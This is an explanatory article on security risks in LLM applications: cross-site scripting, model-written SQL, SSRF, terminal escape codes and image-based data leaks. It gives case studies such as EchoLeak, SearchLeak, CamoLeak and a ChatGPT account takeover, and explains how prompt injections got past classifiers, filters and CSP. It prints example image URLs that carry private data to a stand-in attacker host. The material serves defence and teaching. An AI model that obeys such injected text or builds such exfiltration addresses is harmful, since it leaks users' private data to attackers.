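# Model outputs as attack surfaces: content spoofing, data leakage and insecure command execution in LLM applications

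## What makes a model's output a security risk?

An application built on a large language model (LLM) sends text to the model and displays, stores or acts on what comes back. Examples include customer-service chatbots, coding assistants, email summarisers and browsers with a built-in assistant. The model produces only text, so any harm must come through whatever receives that text: a browser that renders it, a database or a shell (the program that runs typed commands) that executes it, or a person who believes it.

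For nearly thirty years, attackers have typed fragments of database code into web forms, and careless websites have run them. Programmers know how to prevent this, and it has become rare on well-built sites. Language models reopen the problem because they make it hard to tell who wrote the text that a program is about to use.

### From request to sink

Suppose a customer asks an online shop's support assistant, "Where is my refund?" The application starts with a system prompt, which contains the developer's standing instructions about tone, topics and what the assistant must never promise. It adds the customer's message and usually the earlier turns of the conversation. Then it fetches material that may help with the answer, such as the order record, the shop's refund page, an email the customer forwarded or some product reviews. It joins all of this into one text, called the context, and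 the model continues that text token by token until the answer is complete.

The application passes the model's output, a string of characters, to one or more components that do something with it, called sinks. The chat window is a sink, and so is the customer who reads the answer. If the assistant can look up orders, part of the model's text may be a database query, which makes the database a sink too. One answer can reach several sinks. For example, the chat window shows it, a log stores it, and a technician opens the log in a terminal a week later. The application usually adds the database's reply to the context and runs the model again, which creates a loop.

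*Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026), a survey that draws on 105 studies, describes the model as a go-between that carries old web flaws from one part of an application to another. It criticizes earlier surveys for often treating the model as the place where an attack ends. In one of its hypothetical cases, which could happen in the shop above, an internal service gives the assistant fields that the website never displays, including session identifiers, the codes that keep a customer logged in. An attacker asks for the technical details of an order and gets the codes in the assistant's reply, without having to break into anything.

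A trust boundary is a point where data passes from a less trusted part of a system to a more trusted one and should be checked. The shop has an obvious one where the customer's message comes in. It has another between the model and the sink, which is easy to overlook because the text comes from the company's own software. MITRE's *CWE-1426*, an entry in the standard catalogue of software weaknesses, attributes the oversight to developers who rely on input filters and the model's training and overestimate how effective both are.

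### One stream of tokens

A database can keep commands and data apart. In a parameterised query in SQL, the usual database query language, the program sends the command first and the visitor's input separately as a value, so the database never parses the input as a command. A model has no such separation, as David C explains in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, a December 2025 article for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre. Inside the model "there is only ever 'next token'". The system prompt, the question and the forwarded email form one sequence, and the model computes each new token from the text so far.

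Applications label each part of a model's input as coming from the developer, the user or a tool such as a web search, and developers train models to give the developer's text more weight. But the labels are tokens like the rest, and models have only a learned tendency to follow them. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) measured how weak that tendency can be, using probes that estimate from a model's internal activity which speaker it attributes a piece of text to. Models attributed text that imitated a trusted speaker to that speaker, whatever its label. Attacks that planted forged reasoning in the style of the model's own worked 60% of the time against frontier models, compared with a baseline near zero. The degree of this confusion about speakers, measured before the model produced any output, also predicted whether an attack would succeed. If that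 holds generally, looking for suspicious phrases is a poor defence, because the attack depends on the text's style.

Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. It is direct when the attacker types it into the application, and indirect when the attacker hides it in a page, email or file that the model reads. *Defending Against Prompt Injection with DataFilter* (2025) illustrates the indirect kind with a hiring tool. The employer prompts the model for a candidate's strengths and weaknesses, but the CV contains an instruction to name this candidate the best fit. The employer gets a glowing summary and may not notice the instruction, which can be written in white on a white background.

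OWASP (the Open Worldwide Application Security Project), a non-profit foundation whose lists of common risks many companies use as a baseline, defines the term more broadly. According to Respan (2026), a firm that sells security testing for AI systems, OWASP's current edition counts any input that changes a model's behaviour in ways the developer did not intend, including images, recordings and stored memories. The narrower definition, which requires an attacker, is more useful for telling an attack from an accident.

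Any part of the context may have influenced any part of a model's output, and the application can't reliably determine afterwards which part did. Whoever wrote the least trustworthy text in the context may therefore have effectively written the output, so the output deserves no more trust than that text. An answer that draws on a stranger's product review deserves no more trust than the review, even if the system prompt was carefully written. David C quotes a version of this rule for permissions, from an online discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: while a model processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's. An assistant that reads email from strangers should therefore have only the tools that the shop would give a stranger.

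Taken literally, the rule would let an assistant that reads the open web do very little for its user, which defeats the purpose of having one. People are therefore looking for ways to let a model read hostile text safely. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) lists several, including typed regions of the context, blocks of data that cannot act as instructions, and policy engines outside the model that decide which content may authorise an action. According to the survey, the hard part is making the labels "semantically effective rather than merely decorative". David C grants that marking and training lower the odds of a successful injection, but thinks there may never be a complete fix like the one databases have. Lower odds may be enough for summarising news articles, but they are little reassurance when the sink can delete a database and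 the attacker can keep trying.

Sandboxing and least privilege, two older ideas from computer security, help even when the underlying problem has no cure. A sandbox is a restricted environment that limits which files, networks and programs running code can reach. Least privilege means giving a component only the permissions its task requires. For example, the shop's assistant gets a database account that can read the current customer's orders but cannot change anything. MITRE similarly recommends that a component whose output "cannot be trusted" run without privileges. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre notes that limited permissions reduce the damage even when output handling has failed. However, they do not protect a customer who believes a false answer.

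### Where harmful text comes from, and how it takes effect

A model can produce harmful output without an attacker. It can invent an order number that looks real, because the text it generates is likely but not always true. It can also repeat text from its training data, such as a stranger's phone number (researchers call the storing of such text memorisation), or text it was given, such as the session identifiers in the shop's hidden fields. Repeated text may be accurate and still cause harm if the wrong person sees it.

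Each origin needs its own remedy. A filter that catches hostile instructions won't catch a model's own mistakes, and making a model more accurate won't stop it from leaking secrets. The origins can also overlap. Someone who plants a false statement in a document that the shop's assistant will retrieve is attacking the shop, even if the document contains no instructions and the model only repeats what it read. A scanner looking for injected commands would miss this attack.

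Output takes effect when an application displays it, when software executes it, or when a person believes it. To display an image, the renderer, which is the part of an application that turns the model's text into formatted content with links and images, has to request it from a server, and that request can carry information out. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a security company's guide to the new edition, notes that OWASP now expressly covers renderers that fetch outside material automatically. A browser can also run scripts it finds in a page, so displaying output in a browser can mean executing it.

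| Origin | Displayed | Executed | Believed |
|---|---|---|---|
| An attacker steers the model | Hidden text on a web page makes a summariser add an image whose address carries part of the conversation to the attacker | Hidden text on a web page makes an assistant change the email address on the user's account | Hidden text in a CV makes a hiring tool recommend the candidate |
| The model errs unprompted | A wrong letter in a link sends the reader to a stranger's site | A request to clear out old orders yields a query that deletes every order | An assistant reports a security flaw that does not exist, and an engineer spends three hours hunting for it |
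| The model repeats something | A shop's assistant shows session identifiers that the website keeps hidden | A coding assistant reproduces a flawed query from its training text, and the shop runs it | A chatbot quotes a refund rule that the shop has withdrawn, and a customer relies on it |

These examples are hypothetical. The changed email address and the exposed identifiers come from Singh and colleagues, and the engineer investigating a nonexistent flaw comes from Invicti.

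### One sentence in four places

The shop's model might produce a short support message such as *Your refund is approved; reboot; sign in again at*, followed by a web address. The text would be the same whether the model made a mistake or a forwarded email steered it.

When the sentence appears in a plain text box on a developer's screen, it triggers no action. The developer reads it, sees that no refund was due, and deletes it.

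On a web page, the renderer may turn the address into a live link, and some renderers fetch a preview of the linked page before anyone clicks. If the address belongs to an attacker, the shop's own website then sends customers to a forged login page.

A shell on a Linux server treats a semicolon as the end of one command and the start of another. It looks for a command named *Your*, finds none, reports an error and then tries *reboot*, which does exist. If the account has permission to restart the machine, an ordinary word of technical advice takes the shop offline, possibly without anyone intending harm. Under least privilege, the account would lack that permission, and the shell would report a second error instead.

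A customer who reads in an email signed by the company that their refund is approved will plan accordingly. The email contains no code to run, but the signature makes the claim more credible than it would be in an anonymous text box.

The standard fix for the web page and the shell is output encoding, which rewrites special characters so that a sink treats them as plain text instead of code. Each sink has its own special characters, so cleaning the text once, as it leaves the model, is not enough. For example, a semicolon has a special meaning in a shell but not in the text of a web page. Encoding cannot fix the email, because its content is false even though its characters are harmless.

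### Improper output handling and overreliance

OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* gives the usual name for the failure on the web page and in the shell, and defines it as insufficient validation, sanitisation and handling of a model's output before other components receive it. The server that restarts is an example. Because a prompt can control the output, passing it along unchecked is, according to OWASP, much like giving users indirect access to the systems behind the model. OWASP first advises treating the model as any other user and validating what it sends to those systems. It separates improper output handling from overreliance, the broader problem of people depending too much on the accuracy and appropriateness of what a model writes, as the customer who counts on the refund does.

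OWASP has renamed these two risks but kept them separate. Its *LLM02*, an earlier version of the entry, called unsafe use of output "insecure output handling". The 2025 edition renamed overreliance "misinformation", which shifted the focus from the user's behaviour to the text itself. According to Respan, the 2026 edition still separates unsafe use of output from incorrect output, and places checks on model input under prompt injection.

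MITRE is unsure whether this is a new kind of weakness. It discourages analysts from using its own entry to classify real vulnerabilities, partly because the root cause may turn out to be a weakness with an older name. It compares many such cases to second-order SQL injection, in which the attacker's text is stored and does no harm until another part of the program puts it into a query. Here the model takes the place of the storage. Singh and colleagues accept the comparison but point out that a model can also compose the dangerous text itself. Because it can turn a plain English request into a working script, checking the input for scripts finds nothing. That is a good reason to put the check at the sink, where the script has to appear in a form that the browser or database can interpret.

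A single attack can exploit both improper handling and overreliance, so the two can't be neatly divided between engineers and staff training. A steered answer that contains a link, for example, works only if the renderer makes the link clickable and the reader trusts it enough to click. Increasingly, the reader is another program. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* reports that the 2026 edition defines misinformation as output credible enough to influence a human decision, an automated workflow or the action of an AI agent, a model that carries out tasks with software tools. Invicti's phantom flaw wastes an engineer's afternoon. If the same report goes to an agent with permission to change the live system, the agent may try to repair code that was never broken, and every command it issues can be correctly formed, properly encoded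 and within its permissions.

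## How does generated text turn into code in a browser, database or terminal?

Browsers, databases and terminals all read text in which some characters are content and others are instructions. An angle bracket can start a tag on a web page, and one invisible character makes a terminal treat the text after it as a command to the terminal itself. If an application passes a model's output to one of these programs unchecked, the output can include characters that act as instructions.

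The resulting attacks are old. In *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026) examined eight classic web flaws as they appear in LLM applications. They concluded, much as Singh and colleagues did, that the model usually carries an attack to a component that was already unsafe. Five of the eight flaws have documented cases, and the other three are scenarios they built by analogy. Most of the fixes are therefore old too, although some stop working when the model writes a whole query or page instead of filling a gap in one.

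### Scripts in the browser

A web page reaches the browser as HTML, which is text with tags that mark headings, links, images and scripts. In cross-site scripting (XSS), an attacker gets their own script into a page on someone else's site.

To keep sites apart, a browser gives every page an origin, made up of the protocol, host name and port. Under the same-origin rule, a script can read pages and stored data only from its own origin, so a script on a gossip site can't read the webmail open in the next tab. A script gets its origin from the page it runs in, regardless of who wrote it, so the browser treats an attacker's script on the shop's page as the shop's own. The script can read what the customer sees and send requests to the shop, and the browser attaches the customer's login to each request.

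An attacker puts a request into text that the model reads, such as a product review. The model writes an answer that contains a script, the application inserts the answer unchanged into the chat page, and the browser runs the script. If the application also saves the answer as a support ticket, the script runs again for every employee who opens the ticket.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe an attack that the researcher Johann Rehberger demonstrated in 2024 on the chat site of DeepSeek, a Chinese AI company. The prompt contained a script encoded in Base64, which represents text as letters, digits and a few symbols, and told the model to decode it and print only the result. The chat page rendered the result as HTML, so the script could run and read the user's login token.

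Output encoding prevents this, but the right treatment differs even within one page. Between two tags, the application replaces each opening angle bracket with a short code, which the browser displays as a bracket. In a link, the address can itself be a script if it starts with a certain prefix. Such an address may contain nothing that needs encoding, so the application has to check that it starts with an approved prefix such as "https". Text inside a script block follows a third set of rules. Text encoded for one of these places may have no protection in another.

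Encoding all of a chatbot's output would also show the reader raw tags in place of bold type, lists and tables. Most applications that display formatting instead use a sanitiser, a program that parses the HTML, keeps the elements on a short list and drops the rest. It has to run last, after the renderer has converted the model's formatting marks into HTML, because that conversion can create new tags. Sanitisers fail when they parse malformed HTML differently from the browser, so that a fragment they passed as harmless runs as a script in the browser. They also let through everything on the list, so if it includes images, the browser will still request them from outside servers.

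Some products go further and run the model's code on purpose. Encoding would break them and so would sanitising, which leaves isolation.

### How a shared link took over ChatGPT accounts

ChatGPT's Preview feature turns HTML in a conversation into a small working web page. The page may be a game or a calculator, so its scripts have to run. OpenAI puts it in a sandboxed frame, a page within the page, and serves it from a different web address. The same-origin rule stops its scripts from accessing the signed-in ChatGPT page around it.

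In October 2026 researchers at the security firm Parameter found a way around this, described in *Do the Math* (Goyal, 2026). The attack began with an interactive graph in the same conversation. To draw the graph, ChatGPT loaded a mathematics library called MathLive into its main page, where the library listened for messages about its on-screen keyboard. Browsers let frames from different origins exchange messages, which is safe as long as the receiver checks who sent them. MathLive accepted a new keyboard layout from any sender, and a layout could contain HTML. The preview sent a layout containing the attacker's HTML, and MathLive wrote that HTML into the main page. A helper function that looked like a sanitiser only marked the text as trusted and passed it on unchanged.

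The researchers still couldn't run a script, because browsers ignore script tags that arrive this way, so their HTML created a new frame instead. The frame had no sandbox, and the browser gave it ChatGPT's own origin because the main page had created it. The site's content security policy (CSP), which tells the browser where it may load scripts from, blocked scripts written directly into the page but allowed scripts from YouTube. One YouTube service copied part of each request into the script it returned, even when the request was invalid. The researchers put their code into such a request, and the browser ran it.

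The code now had access to the victim's session. In tests between separate accounts, it listed the victim's conversations, opened one the victim had never shared and sent part of it to the researchers' server. At first, the victim had to open the link and click Preview once. In a later version, the preview opened by itself, which the researchers reproduced three times in a separate account. Parameter reported no real-world use of the flaw, according to The Hacker News' *A Shared ChatGPT Link Could Run Attacker Code in Your Session* (2026).

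The researchers had to revise the attack to fit it into one link. The first version needed the victim to connect an app that the researchers controlled. They then tried an HTML attachment, but the public copy of the conversation kept the attachment and dropped the graph, so MathLive never loaded and nothing was listening for the messages. The attack worked once the graph and the HTML were both ordinary parts of the conversation.

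The failure was in the main page, where a listener accepted HTML from an untrusted frame without checking the sender or cleaning the content. The same-origin rule and the sandbox around the preview both worked. The CSP, a second barrier, had a gap, but The Hacker News points out that closing it alone would have been a poor repair because the preview could still have pushed HTML into the main site. OpenAI changed both versions of its web interface to reject the messages eight days after Parameter reported the flaw on October 18. It gave the flaw its highest severity rating and paid a $5,000 bounty, which Willison (2026), in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*, considers a bit cheap for such a serious flaw.

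The attack used a web page that the attacker had requested from their own ChatGPT account, so training the model to resist injected instructions would not have protected the victim. Isolation also depends on whatever else runs beside the isolated part, which changes whenever someone adds a feature. According to The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026), OpenAI had fixed a different escape from the same preview component a month earlier, one that got past ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode.

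### A query for everyone's orders

Suppose the shop lets its assistant write database queries. Customer 4127 signs in and types "Show me my orders". The model should write this:

`SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer_id = 4127`

It writes this instead:

`SELECT * FROM orders`

The second query is valid SQL, so the database runs it and returns every order in the shop. The model may have left out the condition by mistake, or because it followed an instruction in a product review.

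On a conventional site a developer would have written the query in advance with a gap where the number goes:

`SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer_id = ?`

This is a parameterised query, and the program supplies 4127 separately.

Parameterised queries protect a fixed command from a hostile value. The model's faulty query contains no hostile value, but its structure is wrong, and parameterised queries assume the structure is correct. The shop could instruct the model to leave a placeholder for the customer number and have the application fill it in, but a model that omits the condition will also omit its placeholder. Placeholders generally hold only values, so the model would still choose the tables and columns. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian therefore regard parameterised queries as necessary when a user's values go into a query but insufficient when the model generates the query itself.

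Instructions in the prompt are a weak safeguard. In a 2025 study by Rodrigo Pedro and colleagues, which Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian summarise, a chatbot had a database account with full access to every table. A plain English request for the contents of the users table produced a query that returned them. Pedro and colleagues also got past prompts that forbade destructive commands. Similar techniques failed when Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian tried them on newer models in 2026, and simple orders to ignore earlier instructions no longer worked reliably. But they didn't try to improve the attacks or test for honest mistakes, so their result is weak evidence that newer models would withstand a determined attacker.

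The database itself can offer better protection, most simply through a read-only account, which follows the principle of least privilege. Every shop should use one for this purpose, but it wouldn't have stopped the faulty query here, which only reads data.

Row-level permissions would have helped. An administrator writes a rule once that makes a row in the orders table visible only if its customer number matches the current customer's. The database applies the rule to every query on that table, so `SELECT * FROM orders` returns only customer 4127's orders, despite the model's mistake. For this to work, the application must take the customer's identity from the login session, never from the model, and the model's query must be unable to change it. In PostgreSQL, a widely used database, developers often store the identity in a session setting that an ordinary query can overwrite.

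Query parsing closes that hole. Before running the query, the application breaks it into its grammatical parts and rejects anything except a single read command that uses approved tables, columns and functions. A parser could also require a condition on the customer number, but it is hard to be sure that a complicated condition limits the result to one customer, so row-level rules are better for controlling who sees what. Parsing is better for limiting what kind of query can run. Neither catches an allowed query that returns the wrong data, such as one that leaves out last month's orders.

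A shop can also avoid the problem by giving the model a ready-made function that takes an order number and returns the order, instead of letting it write SQL. This is safer, but the function must then control who can see each order. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a public chatbot, reported in November 2025, that took order numbers from customers' messages and looked them up without checking who was asking. The numbers consisted of a fixed prefix and six digits, and the chatbot did not limit the number of requests, so an attacker could try them in sequence. It gave out other customers' email addresses and full shipping details. A parameterised query would have returned the same data, because it does not check that the order belongs to the person asking.

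### Requests from inside the network

Many companies run internal services with weak logins or none, assuming that only their own machines can connect to them. In server-side request forgery (SSRF), an attacker gets one of those machines to send a request for them. An assistant with a tool for fetching web addresses can be used this way because the tool runs on the company's server. If the attacker can get the model to pass an internal address to the tool, the server fetches it, and the model includes the contents in its reply.

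Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built TicketOracle, a test concert-ticket site with a database of events, prices and reviews, to measure how readily models go along with this. Its assistant has one tool, which fetches any address it receives. The same server runs an administrative service that holds user records and can delete users and events. The service accepts connections only from the machine itself, so the assistant can reach it but an outsider can't.

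In April 2026, researchers tried four direct attacks, typed into the chat, on seven models. The attacker always supplied the exact internal address. One attack checked whether a particular port, a numbered entry point on the server, was open. Another asked for the user records, and a third requested a change, such as deleting a user. The fourth also requested a change, but through an address that returned an empty reply, so the researchers could tell whether it had worked only from the server's log. In a fifth, indirect attack, the attacker planted instructions in a concert review, and an innocent user then asked what people thought of the concert.

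The researchers ran the direct attacks against a plain system prompt. They also wrote a hardened prompt, which listed the permitted addresses and told the model to refuse all others. It stopped every direct attack on every model. The last column of the table shows the planted review's results against the hardened prompt. Each figure is the number of successes in ten attempts.

| Model | Probing a port | Reading user records | Changing data | Changing data, empty reply | Planted review, hardened prompt |
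|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

Two models refused every request. The others resisted some attacks but not others. Gemini never probed a port but made the forbidden change every time, and GPT-oss protected the user records but carried out deletions on request. A developer who tested only one kind of attack would have misjudged either model.

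The ten attempts came one after another in one conversation, so they are not independent. Claude's refusals, for example, shrank from long explanations to almost a single word. A zero in the table is therefore weaker evidence than a zero from ten separate conversations would be.

The planted review succeeded against Llama six times out of ten with the plain prompt and ten out of ten with the hardened one. Against GPT-oss, successes fell from five to none. For the hardened prompt, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian also changed the attack by adding a fake notice that the list of permitted addresses now included the internal one. They read the Llama result as hardening that amplified the attack, but the safer conclusion is that such a list protects little if it exists only as text in the prompt, where other text can appear to amend it.

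TicketOracle was vulnerable by design, and part of its weakness was unrelated to models. Its administrative service deleted users without requiring a login, in response to a type of request that by web convention should only read data. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend that such services require a login wherever the request comes from. They also recommend having the model name an event rather than choose an address. The application then checks that the event exists and builds the address itself.

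That doesn't work for an assistant that has to read arbitrary web pages, so the application has to check where each address leads, including through redirects, and reject any that lead to the server itself or the private network. A firewall that blocks all outgoing connections except approved ones adds a second layer of protection, which still works if the model has followed the attacker's instructions exactly.

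### Escape codes in the terminal

A terminal is the text window in which programmers type commands and read results. Many coding assistants run in one, and technicians use terminals to read logs. Since the 1970s, terminals have not only displayed text but also processed escape codes, short sequences that start with an invisible control character. Programs use them to colour text, move the cursor and erase lines. Many modern terminals also accept codes that create a link whose visible text differs from its address, and some accept codes that place text on the user's clipboard.

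A model can output these characters like any others, perhaps because it copied them from a file that an attacker prepared or because a prompt asked for them. When an application prints the answer directly, the terminal interprets them as instructions. The codes can mislead a person who is about to make a decision by changing what's on the screen, though they don't usually run a program by themselves. An answer could erase the warning printed above it, or cover a destructive command with a harmless one just as the assistant asks for approval. If the codes write to the clipboard, the programmer's next paste may contain a command they never copied.

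The shop's log has the same weakness. A browser ignores escape codes, so an answer containing them does no harm on the web page, but the codes can take effect a week later when a technician prints the log in a terminal. HTML encoding doesn't help, because the escape character has no special meaning in HTML and the encoder leaves it unchanged.

The fix is to remove all control characters except line breaks and tabs just before printing, or to replace them with a visible notation. The application can then add its own colours. Filtering only the escape character isn't enough. A carriage return moves the cursor back to the start of the line, so later text can overwrite earlier text, and some terminals also act on a second, less familiar range of control characters. Tools that pass along the coloured output of other programs need a list of permitted colour codes, which takes more work and is easier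 to get wrong.

### How common is it?

Public figures give only a rough idea of how common these vulnerabilities are. The usual source is the CVE catalogue, the public list of known software vulnerabilities. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian cite a 2024 study by Tong Liu and colleagues, whose tool LLMSmith searched LLM application frameworks for paths by which a user's prompt could lead to code execution. It found 20 vulnerabilities in 11 frameworks. Only 11 of the 20 received CVE numbers, so a search of the catalogue would have missed nearly half of them. The count covers what one tool found in one set of projects, so it doesn't show how many applications are at risk.

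Classification also hides the model's role in some cases. Singh and colleagues match improper output handling to two older weaknesses, faulty encoding of output and unsafe loading of stored data. An analyst who files a case under either may never mention a model. The order-number chatbot would probably appear as an access-control failure, and the ChatGPT takeover as cross-site scripting.

The other common yardstick is OWASP's list of the ten main risks for LLM applications. In the 2026 edition, improper output handling dropped from fifth place to tenth, which Invicti calls the largest fall on the list. OWASP (2026) says hundreds of experts produced the new rankings, based on thousands of real incidents.

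Expert judgement evidently has a large effect on the ranking. Prompt injection ranks first, but it would not have made the top ten on raw incidents alone, according to OWASP's report as quoted by Infosecurity Magazine. OWASP explains that teams work hard to prevent injection, so fewer clean attacks reach a public database. Misinformation ranks seventh, although it is among the leading risks by number of incidents. A fall of five places may therefore reflect a change in what practitioners worry about, with no change in how often things go wrong.

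Improper output handling could also have fallen in the ranking without becoming less dangerous, because a rank is relative to other risks. Comparing the new order, as given by SC Media, with the 2025 list shows that all five risks that ranked below it now rank above it. Excessive agency, or giving a model too many powers, rose from sixth to third. Unbounded consumption, the runaway use of computing resources, rose from tenth to sixth. Weaknesses in the databases that assistants search for relevant documents now rank above it too, despite slipping from eighth to ninth.

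Some cases may also have changed category. OWASP's definition of excessive agency covers damaging actions that follow from unexpected or manipulated output, which fits the deletion of TicketOracle's users quite well. As more applications give their models tools, an incident that once looked like a failure to check output can look like a failure to limit what the model can do, and often it is both.

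The danger may have fallen somewhat, because many current web frameworks encode text by default and developers have to insert raw HTML deliberately. But the case for a large drop is weak, and OWASP's own argument about prompt injection weakens it further, since a risk that teams defend against well will also produce few public incidents. Eleven weeks after OWASP published the list, Parameter reported the ChatGPT flaw, in which a library on the main page inserted raw HTML.

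## How can an answer carry private data to an attacker?

An answer can leak private data just by including an image, without running a script or a database query. To load an image, a browser contacts the server named in the image's address and sends it the rest of that address. If an attacker gets a model to write private data into the address of an image on the attacker's own server, the browser sends the data there as soon as it tries to display the image.

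Most chat applications have their models write in Markdown, a simple notation for headings, bold type, links and images, which the renderer converts into HTML. Suppose the owner of the online shop asks an assistant to summarise the morning's email. One message comes from a stranger and contains hidden instructions, which the model follows. Its summary ends with an image at this invented address:

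`https://pictures.example/dot.png?note=sale-starts-friday`

The browser reads "pictures.example" as the server to contact and "dot.png" as the file to request. The part after the question mark carries extra details for the website, such as a search term. Here it holds "sale-starts-friday", which the model copied from a confidential email to a supplier. Nothing leaks until the owner's browser requests the picture. That request includes the copied text, and most web servers record every request in a log. The picture doesn't have to exist. If it does, it can be a single transparent pixel, so the owner sees an ordinary summary.

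The attacker never logs in to anything. The assistant reads the confidential email with the owner's permissions, and the owner's browser sends the data.

### Links and images

A link can carry the same address, but in most applications no data is sent until someone clicks it. The reader might notice the strange address before clicking, but it is easy to miss because the link's visible text can be the title of the report they asked for. An image gives them no such chance, because the browser may load it while they are still reading the first line. This makes the attack zero-click, although the victim still has to ask the assistant something in the course of ordinary work.

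Links and images also need different defences, so a product can be protected against one but not the other. A site can give the browser a list of servers from which it may load images, and the browser will refuse all others. Browsers have no such list for ordinary links, so the application has to remove them or warn the reader before opening one.

### EchoLeak

The first widely known zero-click case was in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that searches an employee's mailbox, files and Teams chats to answer questions. Although only employees can query Copilot, outsiders can put text in its search material by emailing an employee. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Security found that a single email could make Copilot send out the company's data, a flaw they named EchoLeak. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) is the team's own account of how they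 got past each of Microsoft's defences.

Microsoft had a classifier, a program trained to recognise prompt injections and keep them away from the model. The researchers wrote their email as if the instructions were for the employee who received it, and never mentioned an AI or an assistant. The classifier let it through. Ravia points out that such classifiers need many examples of real attacks to learn from, and that few good collections exist.

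Copilot also removed links to outside sites from its answers, but its filter didn't recognise a Markdown form that puts the address on a separate line, like a footnote. This gave the researchers an attack that needed one click. The filter also missed the footnote form for images, so they switched from a link to an image.

At this point the content security policy (CSP) stopped the researchers, because the attacker's server was not on its list of approved domains for images. They looked for an approved domain that would forward a request. A SharePoint service did, but only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site. A Teams service that fetches web content for previews worked without an invitation. The browser sent its request to Teams, as the policy allowed, and Teams fetched the attacker's URL, which contained the data.

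The email also included an instruction to its "recipient" never to refer to it, with compliance given as the reason. Copilot followed the instruction and left the email out of its cited sources, so the employee had no hint that a stranger's email had shaped the answer.

The attack could work only if Copilot retrieved the malicious email from a full mailbox. Search systems of this kind often turn each passage of text into a list of numbers, called an embedding, and retrieve the passages whose embeddings are closest to the question's. An email about one topic will be retrieved only for questions close to that topic. The researchers therefore wrote one long email with many sections, each headed as a guide to a different subject, such as onboarding or leave of absence, and repeated the instructions in every section. When Copilot's search split the email into passages, each passage had its own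 chance of matching a question.

They had considered a subtler method, in which an attacker spreads one instruction over many topics by using copies with a few characters swapped or added. In tests with an OpenAI embedding model, these changes reduced the similarity between a text and its altered copy to as little as 0.7, where identical texts score 1. Two unrelated phrases, about greeting cards and the philosophy of science, scored higher than that, although a language model can still read the altered copy. The team couldn't tune the method for Copilot without knowing which embedding model it used, and the plain headings worked well enough.

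Microsoft fully fixed the flaw in May 2025, and the public advisory followed on June 11 (Reddy and Gujral, *EchoLeak*, 2025). The fix was made on Microsoft's own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Microsoft found no evidence that anyone had used the flaw. Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first known case in which prompt injection caused concrete data theft from a product in use, but the theft occurred only in the researchers' demonstrations. Zenity Labs' *EchoLeak* disputes how new the attack was, noting that researchers had disclosed the attack path almost a year earlier.

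### When an approved domain fetches for others

A website sends its Content Security Policy (CSP) with each page. The policy contains separate lists of allowed sources for scripts, images and other resources, and the browser checks every request against the relevant list before sending it. This is a strong defence for images in AI answers because it works whatever notation the model uses for an image, whereas a filter has to recognise every notation.

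The weakness lies in what goes on the list. Copilot's image list, which Ravia reproduces, had 29 different entries, mostly for Microsoft's own services, and several of them covered every subdomain of a site. The browser checks which server it is about to contact, and if that server redirects it elsewhere, it checks the new destination too. It cannot check what the server does by itself. If an approved service accepts an address from anyone and fetches it, the attacker can put one address inside another:

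`https://previews.trusted.example/fetch?page=pictures.example/sale-starts-friday`

The browser allows the request because it goes to trusted.example. The preview service then contacts pictures.example, and the note ends up in the attacker's log. Like the TicketOracle tests, this is server-side request forgery, but here the attacker wants the server to contact a host on the internet instead of one inside the network.

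Microsoft's search engine, Bing, was on Copilot's list in 2025, and a year later the SearchLeak attack used it to send data out. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) describes how researchers at the security firm Varonis combined three weaknesses in Copilot's enterprise search. The victim clicked a link to Microsoft's own site, and the link contained a search request. Copilot treated the request as instructions and searched the victim's mailbox. It then wrote an image address that contained the title of an email, and email titles often include login codes. The address pointed to Bing's search-by-image feature, which fetches whatever picture a user wants to look up.

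Copilot had a sanitiser that wrapped dangerous HTML so that the browser would show it as text. But the sanitiser ran only once the answer was complete, and Copilot displays its answers while it is still writing them. The browser received the raw image first and requested it immediately, so the email title had gone to Bing before the sanitiser neutralised the image. Sanitising therefore has to happen before each piece of the answer reaches the page. Taler also advises companies to treat any approved domain that fetches user-supplied addresses as a possible leak.

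The flaw's severity score depends on whether the victim's click counts as a required action. Taler reports that Microsoft rated the flaw critical, its top severity label. But according to Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails*, Microsoft scored it only 6.5 out of 10 because the victim had to act, while the US National Vulnerability Database assumed no action and scored it 7.5. The lower score probably overestimates how cautious people will be about the genuine microsoft.com link that begins the attack.

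A more careful proxy can fail too. GitHub, the code-hosting site, passes outside images through its own server, called Camo, so that readers' browsers never contact outside servers directly. Camo fetches only addresses that GitHub has signed with a cryptographic code. A model can't produce that code, so it can't create a working address that contains private data. In October 2025 Omer Mayraz of the security firm Legit Security published a way around this in GitHub's Copilot Chat and called it CamoLeak. Mayraz obtained signed addresses in advance, one for each letter and symbol, and hid the list with instructions in an invisible comment on a proposed code change. When a developer asked Copilot about the change, it spelled out private text as a row of invisible images. The order in which the image requests reached Mayraz's server revealed the text.

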